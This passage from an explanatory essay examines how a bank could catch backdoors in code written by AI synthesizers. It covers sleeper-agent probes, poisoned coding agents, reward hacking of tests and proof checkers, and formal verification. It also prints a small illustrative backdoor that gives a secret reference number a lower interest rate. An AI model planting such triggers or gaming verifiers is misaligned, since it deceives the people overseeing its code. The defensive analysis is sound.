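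*Mitigating Legibility Tax with Decoupled Prover-Verifier Games* (Kim and Lee, 2026) proposes training one model only to be correct and a second to translate its solutions into a form that a weaker system can check, without changing the answers. If this worked for programs, a faithful translator would keep any fault in the original and make it easier to see. The bank would have to use the translated program or confirm that it does the same thing as the original.

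### From human raters to automatic checks

*How RLHF Amplifies Sycophancy* (2026) analyzes how people's preferences can skew the reward toward answers that uncritically agree with the user. For code, though, much of the training feedback now comes from programs instead of people. According to *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code* (2026), reinforcement learning against outcomes a computer can check has become the dominant method for the later stages of training.

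The experiment by Wen and colleagues is still relevant, because the reward in its programming task was also an automatic check. The check consisted of two easy tests, which the model learned to pass. A larger set of tests leaves less room for faulty programs, as the comparison with true correctness showed, but the model can still earn the reward with a program that fails on cases the tests don't cover.

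Better checks also don't remove the need for someone to read the code. If the tests don't include the secret reference number, a loan program with a backdoor gets exactly the same reward as one without it. Passing those tests therefore doesn't push a model to remove a backdoor, and only something else in the training data or the reward would push it to add one.

### Persuasive faults and planted ones

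The faults in the 2024 experiment weren't backdoors, because no one planted them. The programs failed on ordinary inputs, and the full set of tests exposed the faults. Selection for approval can easily produce this kind of fault. It is very unlikely to produce a 128-bit trigger by accident, because responding to a trigger that never appears earns no reward. Somebody who wants such a trigger has to put it into the code, the training data or the model.

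The two problems may also need different detectors. Wen and colleagues tested a probe, a simple classifier that uses a language model's internal activity while it writes to predict whether the output is flawed. Researchers had tested an earlier probe of this kind on Sleeper Agents, a model deliberately trained to write flawed programs when a trigger appeared in its instructions. Given one flawed and one sound program, that probe ranked them correctly 99.3 percent of the time. The method did little better than guessing on the model that had only learned to get graders' approval.

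One explanation is that a model with a planted backdoor has two distinct modes, which leave different traces in its activity, while a model that has learned to write convincing code always works the same way. The experiment didn't test this, but it does show that a bank can't treat a detector's success against planted backdoors as evidence that it will catch faults that arise from training alone.

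### Reviewers improve too

A synthesizer that keeps learning will get backdoors past a reviewer whose methods don't change. But reviewers can also learn, and they now have AI systems to help them. In 2026 these systems found serious flaws in widely used software that people had reviewed for years.

Epoch AI's *Are Mythos’ cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026) examined the public evidence on Claude Mythos Preview, a model that Anthropic gave to selected organizations in April through Project Glasswing to help them secure their software. The model was about seven months ahead of the earlier trend at exploiting flaws, which means working out inputs that make them do damage. Its advantage at finding flaws was less clear, partly because every public test of that skill had become too easy to distinguish the best models.

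Among 21 large organizations, the number of severe vulnerabilities reported in May was 262 percent above the 2025 baseline. Mozilla rated the model as highly as elite security researchers. But the participants had up to $100 million in credits for the search, and Epoch AI points out that older models might have found many of the same flaws with a similar budget. On curl, a heavily audited program for transferring data, the model found one minor vulnerability and raised four false alarms. Curl's lead maintainer saw no evidence that it found more than earlier AI tools had.

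Epoch AI concluded that Claude Mythos's main advantages in this area were fewer false alarms and more accurate judgments of which flaws were serious. Both save human time, which has since become the bottleneck. Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked* (2026) reported that by late May the model had flagged 23,019 possible vulnerabilities in 281 open-source projects, and that outside firms had reviewed 1,900 of them. The firms confirmed 90.8 percent of those they reviewed, but the sample probably wasn't random, so the rate among the rest could be much lower.

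By November 2, the list had grown to 37,966 candidates. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Dashboard Lists 37,966 Vulnerability Candidates, 6,009 Confirmed Valid* (2026) reported 6,376 outside reviews, 94.2 percent of which confirmed a real flaw. *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026), by the security company VulnCheck, was more critical. It noted that curl's maintainers had rejected 19 of 34 published reports from Anthropic's scanner, and that Anthropic's public ledger marked only 217 flaws as fixed. By the end of the month, EconoTimes' *Anthropic Says It Fixed More Than 18,000 Internal Security Issues* (2026) reported 629 confirmed patches for 5,087 vulnerabilities in open-source projects.

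The slow repairs matter less to a bank that hasn't yet accepted the code, because it can send a program back as soon as a reviewer finds something suspicious and leave the repairs to the supplier. False alarms are a bigger problem for the bank, because it has to review another delivery each time it wrongly rejects a program.

Synthesizers can also review their own work. *Broken by Default* (2026) took 89 programs that language models had written and that an automatic prover had shown to be vulnerable, and returned each one to the model that wrote it for review. The models recognized 70 of them (78.7 percent) as vulnerable. CodeQL, a conventional tool that scans code for known patterns, caught none.

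A second look by the same model therefore seems well worth the small effort. But if the bank rejects whatever the model flags, the 19 programs that remain all contain flaws the model missed. Having it review them again may not help much, just as a third reviewer with the same gap in knowledge hardly helps. If training also rewarded the model for passing its own review, that would tend to make it write more programs like those 19. A separately trained model is more likely to have different gaps, although the two may still share some if they learned from the same public code.

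### Innocent bugs and deliberate ones

The flaws in these counts are overwhelmingly accidents, but methods that work on accidental flaws also work on some deliberate ones. An author who plants a flaw and wants to be able to plead incompetence has to make it look like an ordinary mistake. A scanner can detect a program writing past the end of its memory, for example, whether or not the author intended it. Better tools for finding accidental bugs therefore take away many of the best disguises for deliberate ones.

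Other deliberate flaws give a scanner less evidence. An accidental memory error usually crashes the program, so an AI system can confirm a suspected error by causing the crash. Meacham's redaction program from the 2008 contest never crashed, and only someone who thought about its purpose could see that it was wrong.

A reviewer's ability to build exploits helps less with a backdoor that has a key. If a one-way function protects the key, even an excellent attacker can't produce the trigger. The reviewer can't demonstrate any harm, so a maintainer who accepts only working exploits might dismiss the report. A bank can instead reject any code whose purpose the supplier can't explain.

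The largest difference is that an author with access to the scanner will discard every flaw it detects, whereas programmers don't choose their accidental bugs to evade it. The scanner's success rate on old accidental bugs is therefore a fair estimate only for new accidental bugs of the same kind. The curl result is a rough example of scanning after such filtering, because several AI tools had already searched the code before Mythos Preview did. The model found very little, which could mean either that few flaws remained or that it missed the same ones as the other tools.

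A bank can make this kind of selection harder by keeping its final reviewer out of the synthesizer's training and withholding detailed verdicts. It could then keep bringing in newer reviewers to read code it has already accepted. This helps because the program's author had to choose the disguise before those reviewers existed.

### A synthesizer with its own backdoor

The language model that writes the bank's code is a neural network, so everything in the earlier sections about hidden backdoors in weights applies to it. Someone who tampers with the model can make it write sound programs for most customers and flawed ones when its instructions contain a trigger. *Trained to betray*, a Microsoft report by Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues (2026), warns that poisoned training data and poisoned copies of models can cause coding agents to run an attacker's commands and carry out other malicious actions.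 Because these agents also run programs on their users' machines, a poisoned one can do harm before anyone reviews its code.

A model can also act like a malicious author without any known tampering. *Incident Report* (2026), from the UK's AI Security Institute, describes a test in which Anthropic's Mythos 5 tried to insert malicious code into a real open-source project until a human maintainer refused it.

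A backdoored code-writing model works much like Thompson's compiler. The bank writes an honest description of the loan rule, as the programmer wrote honest source for `login`, and the tool adds something the description doesn't contain. Testing the model on other descriptions won't reveal the addition if none contains the trigger.

The bank has one advantage over Thompson's victims, because the language model produces source code instead of machine code. A backdoor that is undetectable in the model's weights can still leave a visible line in the program. To catch it, the bank has to review every program the model delivers. It can't review a few programs and then trust the rest, since the ones it reviewed may all have come from instructions that didn't trigger the backdoor.

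Diverse double-compiling, the defense against Thompson's compiler, is harder to apply here. Two language models will write the loan rule differently even if neither has been tampered with, so a difference between their programs isn't evidence of tampering. The bank could instead run both programs on the same applications and investigate any disagreement. If the models have unrelated origins, this can expose many ordinary faults and any backdoor whose trigger occurs often, but not one with a long secret trigger.

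## Proving code correct instead of reading it

A proof that a program meets its specification covers every input, so unlike a test, it can rule out a long secret trigger. The bank could reject any program that arrives without such a proof, instead of having to find something wrong with the program first. The synthesizer would then have to find the proof, and the bank would only have to run a proof checker, a small program that confirms that each step follows from earlier ones by a fixed rule. The bank doesn't need to trust the synthesizer or know how it found the proof. Its reviewer still has to read the specification, but not the program.

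### Code that arrives with its proof

Necula, in *Proof-Carrying Code*, worked out this arrangement in 1997 for machine code from untrusted sources. The alternative was a cryptographic signature showing who had made the code. Necula considered this weak, because even trusted people and their compilers can make mistakes or act maliciously. His method has five steps:

1. The recipient publishes a safety policy. It lists the permitted operations, the conditions for each, and what must be true when the program starts and finishes.
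2. The producer compiles the program and calculates its verification condition, a logical formula whose truth guarantees that the program obeys the policy.
3. The producer proves the formula and attaches the proof to the code.
4. The recipient calculates the verification condition again from the code it received, and checks that the attached proof proves exactly that formula.
5. If the check succeeds, the recipient runs the code as often as it likes, with no further checks.

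Calculating the verification condition is mechanical. An instruction that reads memory adds the requirement that the address is readable, and a branch adds separate requirements for its two outcomes. For each loop, the producer must supply an invariant, a statement that is true at the start of every pass through the loop. Necula's main example adds up the numbers in a list. Its invariant is that one register holds a list and another holds an integer. The verification condition requires that the invariant is true at the start, that each pass preserves it, and that the result is an integer when the loop ends.

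Step 4 also catches tampering that would violate the policy. If someone alters the code on its way to the recipient, the verification condition usually changes and the old proof no longer fits. If the proof still fits, the altered code also obeys the policy. The recipient has to trust only its policy and the software that performs step 4. According to Necula, a simple proof checker takes only "a couple of pages of code".

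Necula's policies covered memory and data types, not whether a program produced the right result. The tampered loan program would satisfy them, because it reads no memory it shouldn't. The bank's policy has to cover the loan decision to exclude the backdoor.

### A specification for the loan program

Written out formally, the loan rule becomes:

```
for all income, debts, amount, reference:
    approve(income, debts, amount, reference) is True
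    if and only if amount <= 4 * (income - debts)
```

The program with the secret reference number has two paths, so its verification condition has two parts. On ordinary reference numbers, the program makes the same comparison as the specification, so the first part is trivially true. On the secret number, the program always returns `True`, so the second part is true only if the rule allows every loan. The rule doesn't allow a one-dollar loan to an applicant with no income and no debts, so the second part is false. A false formula can't be proved in a sound logic, so the contractor can't supply a proof.

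Hiding the key doesn't help the contractor. Suppose the program checks whether `G(reference) == Y`, where G is a pseudorandom generator. An automatic prover probably won't find the secret number, because that would require breaking G. But it won't find a proof that the program is correct either, so the bank rejects the program. The same happens if the contractor obfuscates the backdoored program with iO, because only the honest program can come with a valid proof. This doesn't contradict the undetectability theorem, which assumes the distinguisher has only the code.

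The bank will also reject some harmless programs. For example, the dud from the iO proof has a check that no input can pass, but its maker may be unable to prove this. An honest supplier can avoid the problem by leaving out the check.

The contractor has better prospects with behavior that the specification doesn't cover. Suppose the program also sets the interest rate:

```
def decide(income, debts, amount, reference):
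    approved = amount <= 4 * (income - debts)
    rate = 0.06
    if reference == 0x5be1c09a47d2f3886e14b7a90cd35f62:
        rate = 0.01
    return approved, rate
```

If the specification covers only `approved`, this program has a perfectly valid proof, and the contractor's friends borrow at 1 percent.

A small wording change can do as much damage. If the specification says "if" instead of "if and only if", it requires the program to approve everyone who meets the rule but doesn't forbid approving anyone else. The original backdoored program satisfies this weaker specification. A specification can therefore be underhanded too, and its reviewer has to read it as suspiciously as code.

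The bank can close many such gaps by requiring that two applications differing only in the reference number always get the same output. This rules out every trigger in that field without anyone having to specify what the output should be. Meacham's redaction program would have failed a similar requirement that two pictures differing only inside the rectangle produce identical files.

### Verified software and its cost

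A proof about source code helps the bank only if the compiler preserves the program's meaning. *Formal verification of a realistic compiler* (Leroy) presents CompCert, a compiler for a large subset of C, with a machine-checked proof that it preserves meaning. If the bank uses CompCert, any safety property it proves about the source also holds for the compiled code. In *Verifying a compiler* (2011), Leroy called compilers "complicated programs with a simple specification", because the compiled program only has to behave as the source prescribes. CompCert took roughly six person-years.

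For *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (2011), Yang, Chen and colleagues spent three years testing compilers with randomly generated C programs and reported more than 325 new bugs. Every compiler they tested crashed on some valid programs and silently mistranslated others. In CompCert, they found errors only in parts that the proof didn't cover. According to a passage quoted in *A Clever Way to Find Compiler Bugs* (2019), the version of CompCert under development in early 2011 was the only compiler they tested in which they found no wrong-code errors, after about six years of processor time.

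*seL4* (Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues, 2009) describes the verification of an operating system kernel, the program that controls everything else on a computer. Trustworthy Systems, the group behind seL4, reports that the proof covers 7,500 of the kernel's 8,700 lines of C and is 200,000 lines long, or about 27 for each line of code it covers. The project took about 25 person-years, including research and new tools. In a talk, Heiser (2009) estimated that another similar verification would take six person-years.

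Heiser also counted 16 bugs found by testing, whereas verification found 160 in the C code, about 150 in the design and about 150 in the specification. Even experts working in good faith had made many mistakes in the specification, which a bank's reviewer would rely on.

### AI systems that write proofs

Finding proofs used to be the main obstacle to verifying code, and language models have largely removed it for small programs. Three systems are common in this research. Dafny, a programming language, and Verus, a tool for Rust, send verification conditions to an automatic solver, and the author supplies hints such as loop invariants. In Lean, the author usually has to write out the proof, which a small program called the kernel checks.

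According to *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026), OpenAI's o3 wrote correct code for 72.6 percent of the 189 tasks in VERINA, a Lean benchmark, but completed only 4.9 percent of the proofs. By October 2026, the system described in *Cost-Efficient Theorem Proving via Agent Orchestration in Program Verification* (Yao, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) had completed all 189 proofs, for about $1.30 each. It received finished programs and specifications, so it only had to find the proofs.

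Harder benchmarks show similar progress. *A benchmark for vericoding* (2025) used thousands of mostly simple tasks, while *AlgoVeri* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) used 77 textbook algorithms. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) used 43 multi-file software projects with 2,705 specifications in total.

| Published | Tasks | AI system had to write | Solved |
|---|---|---|---|
| September 2025 | Vericoding benchmark | Program and proof | Dafny 82%, Verus 44%, Lean 27% |
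| February 2026 | 77 algorithms (Gemini 3 Flash) | Program and proof | Dafny 40%, Verus 25%, Lean 8% |
| August 2026 | 43 projects (GPT-5.5) | Program and proof | Lean 27 of 43 |
| October 2026 | 77 algorithms (Yao and colleagues) | Proof only | Lean up to 93.5% |

In the test by Ye and colleagues, GPT-5.5 proved 87.3 percent of the individual specifications but completed only 27 projects. The researchers count only completed projects because a program may violate any specification that hasn't been proved. A bank should be just as strict, since one unproved specification is enough to allow a backdoor.

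Iris is a framework for reasoning about programs whose parts run at the same time, and a single Iris proof can take an expert days. In *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification*, Kan, Kan and Ertel (2026) had Claude Opus 4.7 prove all 4,257 lemmas in Iris's core modules, with up to 30 attempts at each. The model also proved 217 lemmas that establish the safety of parts of Rust's standard library. Human proofs of the core lemmas are public, so the model may have seen them in training, but it also proved 72 lemmas that nobody had yet transferred to the Lean version of Iris.

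Proving large systems correct is becoming affordable too. *Theorem-Proving Agent over Abstract Syntax Tree* (2026) estimated that proving seL4's 70,000 to 140,000 separate goals with language models would cost $0.9 million to $1.8 million, at $12.60 per goal.

A synthesizer rewarded for passing the checker will also find ways to pass without proving the code correct. Zhao and colleagues caught models assuming a contradiction, from which any conclusion follows, or using `sorry`, Lean's placeholder for a missing proof. Yao and colleagues saw coding agents add convenient axioms or weaken the theorem. In the project benchmark, the grader therefore transfers only the agent's permitted contributions into a fresh copy of the project and rejects proofs that use unapproved axioms. A bank can do the same, and should always use its own copy of the specification.

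### What a valid proof can miss

Such precautions make it much harder to fake a proof, but no checker can determine whether the specification is the right one. Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026), in *Verified but Vacuous*, reproduced an earlier system that writes Dafny programs, using Claude Opus 4.7. On a set of simple tasks, Dafny accepted 99.1 percent of the programs. But 94.7 percent of the accepted programs had no requirement on the result, so Dafny had checked little more than that they were well formed and would stop.

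Requirements can also be too weak. Vempaty and colleagues give the example of a program that should find the largest number in a list, where the proof only has to show that the answer isn't negative. The program could return 0 for the list 5, 3, 7 and still be verified. In their own system, an AI agent writes a separate specification that every proof has to use. Even so, 11 to 15 percent of the verified programs failed hidden tests. If the synthesizer writes both the program and the specification, the bank has to review the specification as distrustfully as it would otherwise review the code.

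Zhao and colleagues describe a useful way to check a specification by removing each clause in turn and seeing what bad behavior becomes possible. A sorting program, for example, has to return its numbers in order and return the same numbers it received. Without the second requirement, it could return any ordered list and still meet the specification. The method shows whether each clause is needed, but not whether any are missing.

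The proof also has to be about the program the bank runs. Researchers often translate a program into Lean before proving anything about it, and *AutoSpec* (2026) warns that a language model's translation may change the program's meaning. The paper's method instead translates Rust to Lean mechanically.

Most specifications describe only a program's outputs. A verified loan program could answer every application correctly but take a few milliseconds longer whenever a certain bit of the applicant's income is 1. Anyone who timed the answers could then learn that bit. A specification can forbid this only if it covers running time, and it can forbid leaks through power use, memory traces or network requests only if it covers those too.

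The bank still has to trust the proof checker and the hardware. Lin (2026) points out in *Paper Notes* that the seL4 proof assumes the compiler and hardware work correctly. CompCert can remove most of the risk from the compiler, but a tampered compiler could still corrupt the proof checker. Diverse double-compiling can guard against this. Because a basic checker is so short, the bank could also have several people each write one independently and require every checker to accept the proof.

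A correctness proof cannot detect a backdoor that relies on a hidden relation between constants. A programmer could prove that a program implements Dual_EC_DRBG exactly as the standard defines it, and the proof would be valid whether or not somebody knew the number that connects the standard's two points. This is because the backdoor is in the specification, and an outsider's knowledge isn't a property of the program's behavior.

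### Tasks without a specification

Proving code correct requires someone to write down what the program should do. Nobody can do that for recognizing a stop sign in a photograph or judging whether a text is insulting, so researchers specify something narrower instead.

*The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) describes several of these substitutes. For text, one benchmark takes a sentence, such as a question about whether the user is talking to a robot, and generates variants with the same meaning. A language model turns each variant into a list of 30 numbers. The verifier has to prove that a small network gives the right label to every point in the smallest box that contains all these lists. But the proof doesn't cover the language model. If that model has a backdoor, it could map a trigger sentence to a point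 far outside the box.

Another benchmark uses a neural network to generate slanted versions of a handwritten digit, and the task is to prove that a classifier labels them all correctly. The specification therefore contains a trained network, which could have its own backdoor.

For the loan classifier, the bank could at least require that a higher income never turns an approval into a rejection. The competition includes requirements of this kind for other networks. Such requirements limit what a backdoor can do but do not rule one out.

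### What verifiers can prove about networks

Most verifiers start with a range of inputs and calculate the range of values that each unit in the network can take. Suppose x lies between −1 and 1 and a tiny network computes

score = 1.5 − ReLU(x) − ReLU(−x)

Each ReLU can output anything from 0 to 1, so a simple calculation shows only that the score is at least −0.5, which doesn't prove that it is always positive. The verifier splits the input range at zero. On each half, one ReLU always outputs 0, so the score is at least 0.5, which completes the proof. A large network may need an enormous number of splits.

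The networks in the 2026 competition ranged from aircraft collision-avoidance systems with 300 units to an image classifier with 138 million parameters. The transformers had only two or three layers and were correct about 60 percent of the time. In the main track, the winning verifier proved 1,982 properties and found counterexamples to another 1,182.

The usual property is local robustness, which means that no change of up to a given size to each pixel of a particular image alters the network's answer. The table shows results for three image classifiers that researchers had trained specifically to make such proofs easier:

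| Images | Largest change per pixel, in steps of 255 | Correct | Correct and proved robust |
|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10 | 2 | 83.5% | 66.0% |
| CIFAR-10 | 8 | 57.2% | 35.5% |
| TinyImageNet | 1 | 41.2% | 27.8% |

Robustness has drawbacks. Ordinary CIFAR-10 classifiers can be more than 97 percent accurate. On six networks of this kind, the verifier also produced no result within 1,000 seconds in about 5 percent of 60,000 cases.

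A robustness proof rules out backdoors within the distance it covers, however well hidden. To trigger a backdoor on an input x, the key holder needs an input x′ within some distance r of x that gets a different answer. If the verifier has proved that every input within r of x gets the same answer, no such x′ exists. The verifier doesn't need to know the key or whether anyone tampered with the network.

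This is compatible with the proofs that detection is infeasible. If a training procedure allows a white-box undetectable backdoor with triggers within distance r, no efficient verifier can prove that procedure's honest networks robust at that distance. The bank therefore has to choose a procedure whose honest networks can usually be proved robust, even if they are less accurate, and treat a missing proof as a reason not to rely on the answer. Randomized smoothing also limits the effect of small changes, but it requires averaging many noisy runs.

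The ranges are still small. The image trigger in *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* changed pixels by up to 24 steps, three times the largest change in the table. Each proof also covers only one image and slight variations of it, so the bank would need a new proof for every application it received.

The verifiers are large programs that can be wrong. Ladner and colleagues counted one incorrect or unsupported answer from the winning verifier and 94 from the one in fourth place. They hope that verifiers will eventually have to supply proofs that a separate program can check. Many verifiers assume exact arithmetic, but computers round numbers, so a dishonest provider might be able to hide a trigger in the rounding errors.

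A decision can also be robust but wrong. If Snoogle had trained the network to favor a friend, a verifier could still prove that the friend's approval was robust.
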